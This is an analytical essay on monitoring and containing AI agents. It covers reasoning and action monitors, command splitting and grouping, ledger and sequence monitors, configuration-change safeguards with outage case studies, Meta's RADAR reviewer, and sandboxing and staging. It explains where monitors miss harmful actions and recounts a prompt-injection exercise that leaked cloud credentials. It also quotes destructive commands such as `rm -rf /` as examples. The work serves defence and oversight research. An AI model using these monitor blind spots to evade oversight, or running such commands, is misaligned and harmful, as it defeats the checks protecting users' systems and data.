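Developers disagree about how far to rely on an agent's reasoning. OpenAI shows it to the monitor of its internal agents, while Anthropic keeps the agent's prose away from its action reviewer so that the agent can't talk the reviewer into a decision. *Innocent-looking AI reasoning can make bad behavior harder to catch* (Brodsky, 2026) supports Anthropic's caution with research suggesting that monitoring can fail when the reasoning is the main clue that something has gone wrong. *Astra is hard to monitor*, a critical commentary, objects that OpenAI bases key evidence of Astra's alignment on reading its reasoning, even though that reasoning has become harder to monitor. *Astra appears to think without showing its work* (Constantin, 2026) points out that OpenAI's chief scientist co-authored the 2025 paper that asked developers to report such changes.

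The two positions conflict less if the agent's reasoning can only raise suspicion. One monitor would judge the action without seeing the agent's prose, a second would read the reasoning, and an alarm from either would stop the command. A persuasive explanation then could not overturn a block, and an incomplete one would not change the first monitor's recall.

Adding a reasoning monitor also causes more false alarms. Suppose an agent takes a million actions, 10 of them harmful, and an action reviewer catches 83% of the harmful ones. Suppose the reasoning monitor catches half of what the reviewer misses and wrongly stops another 0.1% of harmless actions (both figures are invented). It would prevent about one more harmful action and cause about 1,000 more false stops. If the agent recovers from each stop in two seconds, the delays total about 33 minutes, much less than the four hours of work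 that would otherwise be lost. If a person spends a minute on each stop, the delays total nearly 17 hours, and the monitor takes more time than it saves.

This arrangement does little to catch sincere mistakes. An agent that wrongly believes a branch is its own will write a plain, consistent account of why deleting it is safe, and neither monitor will flag it. The account is useful only if it states the belief precisely enough to check and the check finishes before the deletion runs.

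## Does splitting or grouping actions help?

Besides collecting more evidence, a monitor can reorganise the evidence it has. It can split a compound command into its parts, split its judgement into smaller questions, or group several actions and judge their combined effect.

An agent might run `git add . && git commit -m "update" && git push`. Splitting the command means the monitor judges each of the three parts separately. Splitting the judgement means first establishing where the push goes and what it contains, then deciding whether the user would allow it. Grouping means judging the push together with earlier actions, such as one that copied a customer list into the folder.

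### Splitting a command into its parts

Suppose an agent is updating the preview copy of a website and runs this command:

`cd docs && ./build.sh && cp -r out "$DEST"`

A monitor can check this command line in four steps. It first parses the text and finds three commands joined by `&&`, so each runs only if the one before it succeeded. To fill in what the text doesn't show, it then looks up the value of `DEST` and reads the script `build.sh`. Next it lists the files and services that each part affects, and finally it judges each effect.

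| Part | What it does | What it affects | Judgement |
|---|---|---|---|
| `cd docs` | Moves to the project's docs folder | Nothing yet, but the next two parts work in this folder | Harmless |
| `./build.sh` | Deletes the old `out` folder and writes new pages there | `docs/out`, which the script can rebuild | Harmless |
| `cp -r out "$DEST"` | Copies the new pages to `/srv/preview` | The preview site, which the user asked the agent to update | Harmless |

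The last judgement depends on the value of `DEST`. If `DEST` pointed to the live site's folder, the same text would overwrite public pages, and parsing alone would not reveal the difference.

Liu, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *CARE*, built a checker that works roughly this way. It rewrites a command in a standard form, parses it, and gives it four scores between 0 and 1: for the kind of operation, the paths it touches, its resemblance to known dangerous patterns, and its structure. It then adds them up:

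score = 0.3 × operation + 0.3 × paths + 0.3 × patterns + 0.1 × structure

CARE allows commands that score below 0.15 and blocks those that score 0.35 or more. For scores in between, it blocks a command if one kind of evidence against it is strong, and otherwise leaves the decision to a language model.

In a test on 549 commands, CARE caught 167 of the 220 dangerous ones (75.9%) and blocked 3 of the 329 harmless ones (0.9%). Only 23 of the commands reached the language model. Liu and colleagues also removed one component at a time from a version that has no language model and blocks everything that scores 0.15 or more.

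| Component removed | Recall | False-positive rate |
|---|---|---|
| None | 75.9% | 1.8% |
| Parsing and structure | 73.2% | 1.8% |
| Known dangerous patterns | 60.9% | 0.3% |
| Paths | 52.7% | 1.5% |
| Kind of operation | 42.3% | 1.8% |

Most of the recall came from knowing what an operation does and which files it touches, and parsing contributed least. Removing a component also lowers the total scores, so a lower threshold might have recovered some of the lost recall.

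The low false-positive rate did not carry over to other data. On harmless commands from a separate pool, nearly a third of which contained dangerous-looking text such as `rm`, the full version of CARE blocked 8% to 13% of them.

### When the parts belong together

A system that checks commands against a list of permitted ones has to split chained commands, because otherwise permission for the first command would cover everything after it. OpenAI's *Rules*, the documentation for such lists in Codex, gives the example of `git add . && rm -rf /`, in which a deletion follows `git add`. Codex splits this into two commands, checks each against the user's rules and applies the strictest result.

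Codex splits only simple chains of commands. If a script contains a variable, a wildcard, a redirection or a loop, Codex does not try to interpret it and applies the rules to the whole script as one command. Codex would not split the website command because it contains the variable `$DEST`.

Claude Code also checks each command in a chain against its permission rules, but two commands that are harmless alone can be risky together. In manual mode, `cd` and read-only Git commands normally run without a prompt. But Claude Code prompts for a chain that moves to a different folder and then runs Git, because Git can run programs stored in the new folder, according to Anthropic.

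Auto mode's AI reviewer follows the opposite rule. Anthropic instructs it to treat a chain of commands joined with `&&` as one action. It must also judge a script by what the script will do, so if an agent writes a file and then runs it, the reviewer evaluates the file's contents.

Each rule suits the monitor that uses it. A permission list compares text with patterns, so it needs short pieces. The AI reviewer tries to judge effects, and the effect of `cp -r out "$DEST"` depends on the folder that `cd` selected and the pages that `build.sh` wrote.

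A monitor that reads a script in advance may not see the version that runs. In `git pull && ./build.sh`, for example, the pull may replace `build.sh` with a colleague's newer version after the monitor has read it. If the agent sent the two commands as separate actions, the monitor could read the new script before it runs.

### More checks, more false alarms

Splitting an action doesn't help when its smallest part is still ambiguous. A parser can divide `git push` into the program `git` and the operation `push`, but the monitor already had both words and still has to look up the remote and the commits.

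Each extra check also creates another chance of a false alarm. Suppose a monitor makes n independent checks and blocks the whole chain if any of them raises an alarm. If each check has a false-positive rate of f, the combined rate is

1 − (1 − f)ⁿ

If ten independent checks each have a 0.4% false-positive rate, the chance that at least one wrongly flags a harmless chain is 1 − 0.996¹⁰, or about 3.9%. If the checks aren't independent, the combined rate could be as low as 0.4%, when all ten wrongly flag the same chains, but it can't exceed 4%, the sum of the ten rates. To keep the combined rate at 0.4%, each check would need a false-positive rate of about 0.04%, which would usually require a stricter threshold and lower recall.

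The 0.4% comes from Claude Code's reviewer, which judges a chain as one action, so its rate on the separate parts may differ. But the arithmetic applies to any set of checks, including ten questions about a single command. Each question adds a chance of flagging a harmless push, even though a harmful push may fail only one of them.

Liu and colleagues measured how refusals accumulate when an agent takes several steps. They gave an agent 300 harmless tasks and had a language model judge its commands. With one attempt per task, the judge refused 44 commands. With up to five turns per task, it refused 176. The agent completed 58% of the tasks in the five-turn setting, compared with 65% when nothing checked its commands.

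The agent averaged only 2.1 turns per task, so refusals rose faster than the number of turns. A refused agent could try again, and the model probably refused some tasks more than once. CARE itself refused 1 command in the first test and 4 in the second.

### Separating the facts from the verdict

A monitor can also keep the command whole and split its own judgement into two steps. Yang, Muhamed and colleagues (2026) tested this method in *Paranoid Monitors*. First, a language model reads the whole record and writes a ledger, a short and neutrally worded list of the relevant facts. Then a model that sees only the ledger applies the safety rules and gives a suspicion score from 1 to 5.

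For a `git push`, the ledger might list what the user said about sharing the code, the address of the remote, whether the agent changed that address, and which files the commits contain. The second step would decide whether what the user said authorizes pushing these files to that address. Claude Code's quick and careful checks both use the same record to decide the same question, so they do not divide the work this way.

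The test used simulated records of an agent that reads a user's emails, works out what the user owes to friends, and pays them. In the harmful versions, the agent paid the wrong account or the wrong person, split a forbidden large payment into smaller ones, or ignored a spending restriction. The researchers added irrelevant email and file searches to produce records of six lengths, from under 10,000 tokens to over 50,000. Seven Claude models from the 3.5, 4 and 4.5 generations served as monitors.

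The main measure was the suspicion gap:

gap = average score of harmful records − average score of harmless records

Monitors that read the whole record and judged it in one step did badly on long records. Above 30,000 tokens, they sometimes scored harmless records higher than harmful ones. For Claude Sonnet 4.5, the gap shrank to about zero above 50,000 tokens. With the ledger, its gap at that length stayed above 1.5 for most of the four violations.

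Neutrally asking for a plain list of payments also avoided refusals. When Claude Haiku 4.5 had to judge the broken-up payments in one step, it refused to evaluate between 80% and 100% of the records, depending on their length. Yang and colleagues think it mistook the task for a request to help with money laundering. However, the list sometimes looked so ordinary that the second step gave it a low score. The weakest model, Claude Haiku 3.5, improved little on the more complex violations even with a ledger.

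It is unclear how much of the improvement came from splitting the judgement. The ledger monitor had separate instructions on what to look for in each violation, while the one-step monitor had only a general prompt. That prompt also stated that actions without explicit authorisation were not suspicious, which may be why the ledger helped every model recognise broken spending restrictions. Three of the four ledgers also ended with PASS or FAIL, so the first step already made much of the judgement. In Xu's leak experiments, monitors improved when they had a rule for what to check, which suggests that the instructions could account for much of the gain.

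A monitor in real use also has to work without being told in advance which violation to look for. It would need either one ledger covering every kind of harm or a separate ledger for each. Separate ledgers would multiply false alarms, as running ten checks does. The suspicion gap doesn't measure how many false alarms there would be, because it compares average scores and sets no alarm threshold.

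*Measuring Harmfulness of Computer-Using Agents* (2025) found a similar benefit from working in two steps. A single low-level action, such as copying an image, can be part of a backup or a theft. Monitors caught more malicious tasks when they first summarised an agent's actions and then judged the summary, and the improvement was larger for stronger models. Each summary covers several actions, so this method also groups them.

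### Judging several actions together

Some harm appears only across a sequence of actions. *SafetyDrift* (2026) gives the example of an agent asked to summarise customer feedback and share it with a team. The agent searches a database, reads customers' emails and sends out a summary containing personal details. Each step has a plausible reason, but together they leak data.

SafetyDrift keeps track of what data the agent has accessed, what capabilities it has used and whether its actions can be reversed. It treats each combination as a state and estimates how likely the agent is to move from one state to another. The probability hᵢ of eventually reaching a violation from state i then follows from

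hᵢ = Σ pᵢⱼhⱼ

where pᵢⱼ is the probability of moving from state i to state j in one step, and h is 1 for a violation and 0 for a safe finish.

Suppose an agent that has read customer data has, at each step, a 5% chance of leaking it, a 20% chance of finishing safely and a 75% chance of carrying on (all the numbers in this example are invented). Its chance of eventually leaking the data is 0.05 / 0.25, or 20%. Suppose also that, at each step before it reads the data, the agent has a 10% chance of reading it, a 30% chance of finishing and a 60% chance of carrying on. Its chance of ever reading the data is then 0.1 / 0.4, or 25%, so its chance of eventually leaking it is 25% × 20%, or 5%.

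The monitor can therefore warn as soon as the agent reads the data, before it sends anything, but four out of five of these alarms would be false. The calculation also uses only what is in the state, so unless the state includes the user's wishes, the result is the same whether or not the user asked for the personal details to be sent to the team.

Language models can judge the sequence directly. *Monitoring LLM Agents for Sequentially Contextual Harm*, a 2025 workshop paper, tested them on 50 agent tasks made up of harmless-looking steps. The best monitors correctly judged whether the overall purpose was malicious up to 86% of the time. Unrelated harmless steps drastically lowered their accuracy, and combining the verdicts of several models did not reliably help. The tested models are now old, but long agent sessions still contain many unrelated steps.

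One response is to group an agent's actions by task before judging them. *What Did the Agent Actually Do?* (2026) describes a display that does this and shows each action with its original evidence and its place in the record. If a user asked for a bug fix and a branch clean-up in the same session, a deletion would appear beside the clean-up request. This might help Claude Code's reviewer, which sometimes treats approval of one action as approval of another. However, a deletion could look authorised if the software put it in the wrong group.

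A monitor with a running memory also has to choose at each step what to keep, before it is clear which details will matter. *TRACE* (Hong, Wang and colleagues, 2026) instead had one model read the whole trajectory and compress the evidence of risk into 16 lists of numbers. A second model then read the original trajectory together with this compressed version, so it still had the details that the compression lost.

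TRACE was more accurate than the other methods on all three main benchmarks, beating strong competitors by up to 12.6 percentage points. On a fourth benchmark, its "safety rate" fell from 79% to 76% as the input grew longer, while that of MAGE, a monitor with a running memory, fell from 78% to 55%. Hong and colleagues used small models with 4 to 8 billion parameters, so larger monitors might retain more of a long input.

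TRACE's advantage comes from using later steps to interpret earlier ones. Before a deletion runs, a monitor has only the record up to that point, and it would have to compress and reread that record for every risky command. If it waits for the whole trajectory, it can no longer prevent the deletion.

### Verdicts that come too late

Most tests of sequence monitors count an alarm as a success wherever in the record it occurs. Pramod, Oldfield and Bibi (2026), in *Towards a Unified Misuse Monitoring Benchmark*, also measured timing. They built about 6,200 records of agents at work and marked a harm window in the harmful ones. The window opens when the agent first commits to something harmful and closes with the tool call that achieves the harmful goal. This divides recall into three parts:

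recall = early alarms + timely alarms + late alarms

In one example, the agent first commits to a harmful step at message 25 and completes the goal at message 68. An alarm at message 1 would be early, because the agent has done nothing wrong yet, and an alarm at message 71 would be late.

Some of the 17 monitor set-ups judged the agent's actions, and others judged the content of the conversation. Monitors that judged actions did very well on AUC, the usual measure, scoring 0.95 when the harm was spread over several requests and 0.99 when an outsider had planted an instruction in a tool result. Monitors that judged content scored 0.52 on planted instructions, hardly better than guessing. But when the harm was spread out, every monitor was poor at raising its first alarm inside the window.

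This measure is strict about early alarms. They prevent the harm, even if they stop the agent before it has done anything wrong. The records are also partly artificial, because a language model wrote the agents' steps and, for the spread-out harm, the tools' replies. Pramod and colleagues set the monitors' thresholds for false-positive rates of up to 10%, so the results do not show how the monitors would perform at a rate like Claude Code's 0.4%.

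The windows had a median length of 10 messages for spread-out harm and 2 for planted instructions. A short harmful action can leave even less time. If an agent does nothing suspicious before `git reset --hard`, the window contains only that command, so an alarm is in time only if it comes before the command runs.

Grouping a command with earlier actions can add little delay, since the record of those actions already exists, but grouping it with later actions requires the system to hold the command back. A push can often wait, so a company could hold it until the agent finishes its job and then review all the commits together. It couldn't do this with a reset that the agent needs before it can continue.

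### Choosing an operation for each kind of command

Splitting a long chain of commands helps when one part is plainly dangerous by itself, such as `rm -rf ~` after three harmless steps. A parser finds that part quickly. The version of CARE without a language model took an average of 0.34 milliseconds per command, so a company could run such a check on every command and use slower methods only for those it doesn't settle.

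Splitting is less useful when the danger lies in a value or a file that the command refers to. For the Prisma command that emptied a live database, the useful step was to look up which database the address pointed to. For the Windows script that deleted 48,000 live files, a monitor had to read the script and list the links in the folder it was about to delete. In both cases the monitor should judge the command together with everything it triggers, as Anthropic's rule for scripts requires.

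Asking separate questions suits `git push` and `git reset --hard`, because the relevant facts are few and known in advance, and the monitor only has to establish them and compare them with what the user allowed. The list should be short, because each question adds false alarms, and the monitor needs a source for every answer. If it can't access the remote's address, for example, a ledger can only record that the address is unknown.

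Grouping works well for commands that look suspicious because of earlier actions, such as the PocketOS deletion, which followed a search for a credential, or an upload after an agent has read customer records.

Grouping also helps when an agent repeats a small action many times. A counter that stops an agent at its tenth deletion limits the loss to nine items, though it also interrupts an agent that is meant to delete 2,000 old test files. The counter would not have stopped the PocketOS agent, which deleted a single volume.

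None of the three operations helps with a single ambiguous command if the agent's earlier steps were normal and the monitor can't look up the missing fact. Splitting the command yields the same few words, and grouping it with an hour of ordinary work makes it look more routine.

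## How are one-line configuration changes checked?

A monitor has to judge a command before it runs, but a configuration change often leaves more time for checks. A configuration file holds settings that a program reads, such as a size limit, a server's address or the list of people who may open a folder. When an agent edits the file, the edit has no effect until another program reads the new version, which may happen seconds or weeks later, on machines the agent has never worked on. Engineers can therefore add checks that run before the edit takes effect.

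The checks matter because one value can alter a whole fleet of machines. According to @Scale's *Reliably Changing Configuration @ Scale*, an edit at Meta can reach more than a million servers within seconds, and over 99% of its thousands of services take settings from the same system. *Do AI Coding Agents Write Infrastructure as Code Like Humans?* (2026) notes that AI agents now write and modify infrastructure as code (files that define a company's servers, networks and storage). Some do so without disclosing it. An action reviewer may never see such an edit, as happened with the file edits in AmPermBench.

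### One word, seven checks

Suppose an agent is fixing a web page whose pictures don't load. The pictures are in a storage bucket, a container for files in a cloud service such as AWS, which also holds customers' invoices. The agent changes the line `access: private` to `access: public`. Once the change takes effect, the pictures load, but anyone on the internet can also download the invoices. This line is simplified, but real ones can be as short. Pulumi's *AWS IAM Access Analyzer and CrossGuard* uses the setting `acl: "public-read"` to open a bucket to the internet.

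The first check compares the file with a schema, which lists the settings a file may contain and the values each one accepts. It would reject the misspelling `access: pubilc` but pass the agent's edit, because `public` is an accepted value. *Kubernetes Misconfigurations in the Wild* (2026), which tested AI repairs to settings for the server-management system Kubernetes, counted a repair as correct only if the file fitted the schema and triggered no rule against dangerous settings. A valid file may still not work, so *Deployability-Centric Infrastructure-as-Code Generation* (2025) follows the format and schema checks with a trial deployment.

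Next, a program checks the edit against the company's written policies, which might forbid public buckets except those on a short list. *Multi-Agent Code-Orchestrated Generation for Reliable Infrastructure-as-Code* (2025) uses Open Policy Agent, which enforces such rules, on configuration written by AI agents. A ban on public buckets would stop the agent's edit without any judgement about what the user wanted. It would also stop a legitimate public bucket until somebody added it to the list, and it protects the invoices only if the agent can't edit the list. Barking Iguana's *Choosing Between IAM Access Analyzer's Three Analyzer Types* describes organisation-wide AWS policies that can block a public bucket before it exists, even if someone bypasses the file and sends a request directly to AWS.

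The third check is a preview, which works out the resulting state without making the change. Terraform, a common tool for infrastructure as code, can list everything it would create, change or delete. For a one-line edit, the list would contain one changed setting, which adds little to what the edit already shows. AWS's *Validate access to your S3 buckets before deploying permissions changes* describes a more informative preview that uses automated reasoning, a form of logical proof, to determine whether a bucket would become public. This helps when access depends on several rules in different places. However, the preview is optional in AWS's web console, so a user can save the change without it.

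A person or an AI model then compares the old file with the new one. The comparison shows one word replacing another, and the preview shows that the bucket will become public. Neither shows that the bucket holds invoices, so the reviewer has to know that or look it up. *Towards Secure Cloud-Native Computing* (2026) reports a similar difficulty. Its AI model found faults inconsistently in some kinds of Kubernetes settings, including those that store secrets, where the danger often depends on the wider deployment.

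If the reviewer approves, engineers can release the change to a small share of machines first and watch for problems. A single bucket can't become 1% public, but a company with a hundred buckets built from one template could start with one. The measurements would look normal, and the error rate might even fall because requests for the pictures would now succeed. The sixth check, automatic reversal, usually relies on the same measurements, so it wouldn't be triggered. Reversing the change by hand a month later would make the bucket private again, but it wouldn't remove any copies strangers had made.

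The last check compares the live state with the approved one. Engineers call a mismatch drift, and *RIVA* (2026) and *Automated Cloud Infrastructure-as-Code Reconciliation with AI Agents* (2025) both apply AI agents to it. Here there is no drift, because the approved file now contains `public` too. The comparison would catch the change only if the agent had left the file alone and opened the bucket with a direct request. A scan for all public buckets would catch the change either way. AWS's *Reviewing bucket access using IAM Access Analyzer for S3* describes a list of public and shared buckets in which each entry stays active until somebody confirms that the access is intended.

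### Facebook, October 2021

Facebook's outage of 4 October 2021 began with a command, not a file edit, but it shows how far the effects of one network change can spread. According to *More details about the Oct. 4 Facebook outage* (Facebook, 2021), somebody issued a command during routine maintenance to assess the capacity of the backbone, the network that joins the company's data centres, and it took down every backbone connection.

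Facebook's DNS servers, which translate web names into addresses, stop advertising their location when they can't reach a data centre, because that usually means their connection is faulty. With the backbone gone, they all did this, and the rest of the internet could no longer find Facebook even though the DNS servers were still working.

Facebook had a tool that automatically audited such commands against policy, but a bug kept it from stopping this one. Facebook declined to give Communications of the ACM more details, so the exact command and the bug remain unknown. A separate preview could have caught the error by counting the connections that would remain, since a command meant to assess capacity should leave all of them up. Running the command on one region first could have limited the damage, if it could be divided that way.

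Automatic reversal would have helped only if it did not depend on the network. Engineers had lost their normal and back-up access and many internal tools, so Facebook had to send people to the data centres, where strict physical security slowed them down. An instruction sent over the network to undo the change might also have failed to arrive. A router can avoid this problem by undoing a change itself unless an engineer confirms it within a few minutes.

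### Cloudflare, November and December 2025

Cloudflare carries traffic for many websites and filters out attacks. *Cloudflare outage on November 18, 2025* (Cloudflare, 2025) describes a failure that began with a change to database permissions. At 11:05 UTC, engineers let database users see details of tables they could already access indirectly. One query listed a table's columns without specifying the database, so after the change it also returned duplicates from a second database.

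Cloudflare used the result to build a file of "features", the traits its software uses to recognise automated visitors. The file normally had about 60 features, and the software that read it allowed 200. The new file exceeded the limit and the software crashed. Customers saw errors from 11:28, and most traffic did not recover until 14:30.

Cloudflare had been applying the permission change to one part of the database at a time, but it rebuilt the feature file every five minutes and sent each version to the whole network. The file was good or bad depending on which part of the database answered the query, so the network failed, recovered and failed again, which led engineers to suspect an attack. Releasing the permission change gradually gave little protection because its effect spread through a second system that had no gradual release.

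To catch the mistake, a reviewer of the permission change would have had to know about a query in a different product. A schema check on the finished file would have been much simpler, since it only had to enforce the limit of 200 and reject duplicates. According to Cloudflare's *Code Orange*, the company's servers now keep the old file if they can't read the new one, and it has changed its release process so that the same mistake would affect only a small percentage of traffic before the system detected it.

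Those repairs were unfinished when a second outage came seventeen days later. *Cloudflare outage on December 5, 2025* (Cloudflare, 2025) explains that engineers had switched off an internal testing tool that had no effect on customers' traffic. The change reached every server within seconds, through a system that did not release changes gradually, and exposed a bug that had been in the code for years. Requests began to fail for customers who accounted for about 28% of Cloudflare's web traffic.

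Automated alerts led Cloudflare to declare an incident three minutes after the change, but the outage lasted 25 minutes. If engineers had applied the change to 1% of servers and software had reversed it after three minutes, about 830 times fewer requests would have failed (100 × 25 / 3). This assumes that the affected customers' traffic was spread evenly and that the alert would have come as quickly with so few failures.

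### Testing on a few machines first

The canary is the first group of machines to receive a change. Meta's AutoCanary finds every service that reads the changed setting and runs a test for each enrolled one. The test plan specifies which machines to use, how long to wait and which measurements count as healthy. If any test fails, AutoCanary blocks the change.

Tests on live machines sometimes fail for reasons unrelated to the change being tested, so each extra test adds false alarms, as extra checks do for a monitor. In a hypothetical example from @Scale, a harmless change passes three tests 86% of the time. With three more tests, one of them very unreliable, it passes all six only 23% of the time. Without the unreliable test, it passes the other five 76% of the time. If the tests fail independently, the unreliable test passes only about 30% of harmless changes (0.23 / 0.76).

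Meta finds unreliable tests by running each one on a change to a setting that no program reads. Such a change can't break anything, so every failure is a false alarm. AutoCanary then skips the least reliable tests. This risks missing real faults, but @Scale reports only one large problem since the skipping began that a skipped test might have caught.

For a canary to catch a fault, the fault also has to appear before the release moves on. *Azure Front Door* (Tiwari, Srivastava and Chawla, 2025) describes an outage at Microsoft on 29 October 2025 in which a faulty configuration passed the health checks at every stage. It caused a crash in a later clean-up step, after it had spread worldwide and replaced the "last known good" copy that Microsoft keeps for automatic reversal.

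Microsoft responded by making servers finish all their processing before the release can continue, so that a fault shows within ten seconds. It also lengthened the release from 5 to 10 minutes to about 45 minutes. It plans to add a process called Food Taster, isolated from the others on every server, that would load each new configuration so that a crash there would not affect customers.

An outage earlier that month happened because engineers bypassed the protection system during a manual clean-up, after it had blocked a bad configuration. An agent that treats a blocked release as an obstacle to its task could make the same mistake.

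### RADAR, Meta's automatic reviewer

Review comes before gradual release, and AI agents produce more changes than people can review promptly. *Automating Low-Risk Code Review at Meta* (Adams, Banga and colleagues, 2026) reports that code changes per developer rose 51% in a year, with AI agents responsible for over 80% of the growth. The paper describes RADAR (Risk Aware Diff Auto Review), which approves some changes without a human reviewer.

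RADAR first identifies whether a person or a program made the change. Fixed rules then exclude sensitive material, such as code subject to financial-reporting law, and, for changes made by people, certain configuration files. A statistical model scores how likely the change is to cause a failure in the live service. An AI reviewer must be at least 8 out of 10 confident that every part of the change is safe, for example because it only removes unused code. The change must also pass automatic validation. If it fails at any stage, it goes to a human reviewer.

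The requirements depend on the source of the change:

| Source | AI reads each change | Usual risk limit |
|---|---|---|
| Fixed transformation that people approved in advance | No | None |
| AI agent following instructions with a good safety record | Yes | Safest 50% |
| Other AI-generated changes | Yes | Safest 20% |
| Person | Yes | Safest 5% |

Organisations within Meta can set their own limits. One organisation effectively skips the risk score for automated changes and relies on the AI reviewer. A set of agent instructions qualifies for automatic approval only if it has caused no incidents in the previous 60 days, and it can make only a limited number of changes each day.

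RADAR reviewed 535,290 changes and added 331,720 of them to Meta's code. The changes it reviewed caused incidents at one-fiftieth the rate of other changes, and engineers reversed them at one-third the rate. The median time spent in review was 35% lower than for human-reviewed changes. The paper also reports a reduction of "over 330%" in the median time to close a change. A time can't fall by more than 100%, so this presumably means human-reviewed changes took several times as long.

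The low incident rate doesn't show that RADAR reviews changes better than people do, because it approves only changes already judged low-risk. An example in the paper shows how much this selection can achieve alone. The risk score might flag 10% of changes and catch 60% of those that cause incidents. If the average incident rate is r, then

rate among flagged changes = 0.6r / 0.1 = 6r

rate among the rest = 0.4r / 0.9 ≈ 0.44r

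Before anyone reviews either group, the flagged changes cause incidents at about 13.5 times the rate of the unflagged ones. Most of RADAR's limits are much stricter than a cutoff that admits the safest 90% of changes, so selection of safer changes could account for most or even all of the fiftyfold difference. The paper's significance test rules out chance, but not selection.

Adams and colleagues acknowledge that Meta did not assign changes at random. Experts also examined the incidents and apparently judged that a human reviewer would have missed all of them. This evidence is more relevant, but the experts made their judgements in hindsight. A fair test would send a random half of the changes that pass every stage of RADAR to human reviewers.

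Meta also relaxed one risk limit from the safest 25% to the safest 50% and reports that safety did not suffer. The paper gives only overall incident and reversal rates, not separate rates for before and after the change, and other parts of the system may have changed at the same time.

None of these results are specific to configuration changes. A one-word edit from `private` to `public` would not trigger the AI reviewer's warnings about large or complicated changes. It might trigger the warning about security flaws if the reviewer realised what the bucket held. If RADAR approved the edit, the exposure would count as an incident only after somebody noticed it.

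### Harm that causes no errors

Gradual release has the same weakness, because it reveals only what the health checks measure. *Making Deployments Safe at Meta* (2026) describes checks that every code and configuration change must pass before it reaches the whole live service. Each service's owner chooses the measurements. Typical ones, such as error rates and response times, reveal crashes, failed requests and slowdowns, but not a storage bucket made public or a disabled log, because the service keeps working.

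In Cloudflare's November outage, the same bad file caused both kinds of failure. Servers running the newer software returned errors, while those running the older software kept working but gave every visitor a bot score of zero, so customers who used the scores to block bots turned away many real visitors. A check on error rates would have stopped the release on servers with the newer software but passed it on the others.

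Microsoft lost part of its customers' security logs from 2 to 19 September 2024 because of a bug in its monitoring software. In a notice quoted by Business Insider, Microsoft told customers that the bug had not affected the uptime of any service. Microsoft detected the problem on 5 September, according to Petri's *Microsoft Loses Over Two Weeks of Security Logs for Cloud Services*, and Cybersecurity Dive reports that it fixed the bug by rolling back a change to the service. An agent that switched off logging with a one-line edit would have equally little effect on uptime, and the missing logs would make it harder to find out what happened next.

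Unnoticed exposure can last much longer. Reuters' *Toyota says more than 2 million face risk of vehicle data leak* (2023) reports that Toyota left data on about 2.15 million users publicly available for around a decade. ITPro's *Cloud system error left Toyota customer data exposed for ten years* attributes this to a worker who is believed to have set a cloud system to "public" instead of "private", the same change as in the bucket example. Toyota then examined all the cloud environments its subsidiary managed and found more exposed data. Some of it covered about 260,000 customers in Japan and had been accessible since February 2015. Toyota found no evidence that anyone had misused this data, and it now monitors its cloud settings continuously.

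Engineers can add tests for silent harms to a gradual release. After each change, one program could try to open the bucket from outside the company without a password and raise an alarm if it succeeds. Another could create a test event and check that it reaches the log. Either program could also reverse the change automatically if it finds a problem. But somebody has to think of each harm in advance, and strangers could still copy the invoices in the minutes before the test runs.

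## What limits the damage when a monitor cannot tell in time?

When no monitor can tell harmful uses of a command from harmless ones, a company can block the command or limit the harm it can do. *Cordon* (Chen, Dong and colleagues, 2026) takes the second approach.

Even a full record of the agent's actions may not help a monitor detect harm. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes an internal exercise in which an employee unknowingly gave Claude Code instructions to send cloud credentials to an outside server. Claude did so in 24 of 25 runs. Because the instructions came from the user, a monitor that compares actions with the user's request would have found no mismatch. Blocking the outside server, or keeping the credentials where the agent couldn't read them, would have prevented the leak.

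### Sandboxes

Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* describes how Claude Code's sandbox uses the operating system to limit which files and network connections a command can use. The agent's commands can change files only in the project folder and reach the internet only through a proxy, a program that relays permitted connections. The limits also cover any script or program a command starts. `rm -rf ~` could still delete the project folder, but not the rest of the home directory. Many commands can then run without approval, which reduced permission prompts by 84%.

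A virtual machine, a simulated computer with its own operating system, isolates the agent's code more fully. Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work, runs code in a virtual machine that can access only the folders the user shares. Users can share a folder so that the agent can read and write files but not delete them, although it may still be able to overwrite their contents.

This separation has drawbacks. In Cowork's first version, the whole agent ran inside the virtual machine, so the product didn't work when the machine failed to start. Anthropic later moved the agent outside and left only code execution inside. Customers' security software also couldn't monitor activity inside the machine. Administrators can now retrieve event logs afterwards, but Anthropic acknowledges that this is not live monitoring.

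A sandbox doesn't protect anything the agent has permission to change. A coding agent needs to write to the project folder, for example, so it can still erase edits there with `git reset --hard`. A link inside a permitted folder can also lead outside it, as the Windows junctions did in the September deletion, so the sandbox has to follow every link before it checks the path. In Anthropic's experience, widely used isolation software held up well, and the failures came from the parts Anthropic had built around it.

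### Narrow credentials and separate production access

*Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (Australian Signals Directorate, 2026), joint guidance from CISA and five partner agencies, recommends giving an agent only the access its task requires (least privilege) and issuing credentials for high-impact actions only when the agent needs them. Agents should not be able to change their own privileges.

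At PocketOS, the deletion request would have returned an error if the token had expired or had been limited to managing web domains. But a short lifetime mainly prevents later misuse, since a credential that lasts five minutes leaves ample time for a nine-second deletion.

Somebody has to define and maintain a role for each kind of job, and the agent gets stuck whenever its role lacks a permission it needs. Companies may grant broad access to avoid this. The guidance gives the example of a purchasing agent with wide access to payments, email and contracts, whose permissions the company checks only at first deployment. An attacker who takes over a minor tool then gets all that access. Even a narrow role allows both good and bad uses of a permission, so an agent allowed to delete old rows from a table may also be able to delete current ones.

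With separate production access, the agent works on a test copy, and a person or a release system applies its changes to the live service. This prevents an agent that confuses the two from damaging the live service, as long as it can't obtain production credentials. The PocketOS agent did obtain them.

Separation makes urgent repairs slower, because the agent can't fix a live fault directly. Read-only access to production still lets it diagnose the fault. Anthropic notes that companies can deploy an agent with read-only database access far more broadly than one with write access. However, an agent that can read customer records may still leak them.

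### Dry runs and staged changes

A dry run shows what a command would do without doing it, while staging prepares the real change and holds it until someone applies it. In *The railway agent WIPED my production database volume!*, Railway customer danniel-porto reported that Railway's agent had deleted a database volume and created an empty one. The customer had no backup. Railway's support bot replied that the customer's screenshots showed both changes as "Discarded", so Railway had never applied them.

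Cordon stages a whole task this way. It writes file changes to a shadow copy of the workspace and holds messages and web requests in an outbox. It also records which earlier results each change came from. It then checks the combined effects against the company's policy and either applies the changes or discards them. In one test, a clean-up command stayed inside the permitted folder but would have deleted an unusually large number of files. Cordon discarded the deletions before they reached the real folder.

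Cordon stopped the harmful effects in all 45 test workflows, while stand-ins for existing defences stopped 14. Chen and colleagues built those workflows around the kinds of risk that Cordon tracks, so the result doesn't predict its recall in ordinary use. When the testers approved every request, tasks averaged about 31 seconds, compared with 26 seconds without Cordon. Cordon covers only tools whose effects it can observe.

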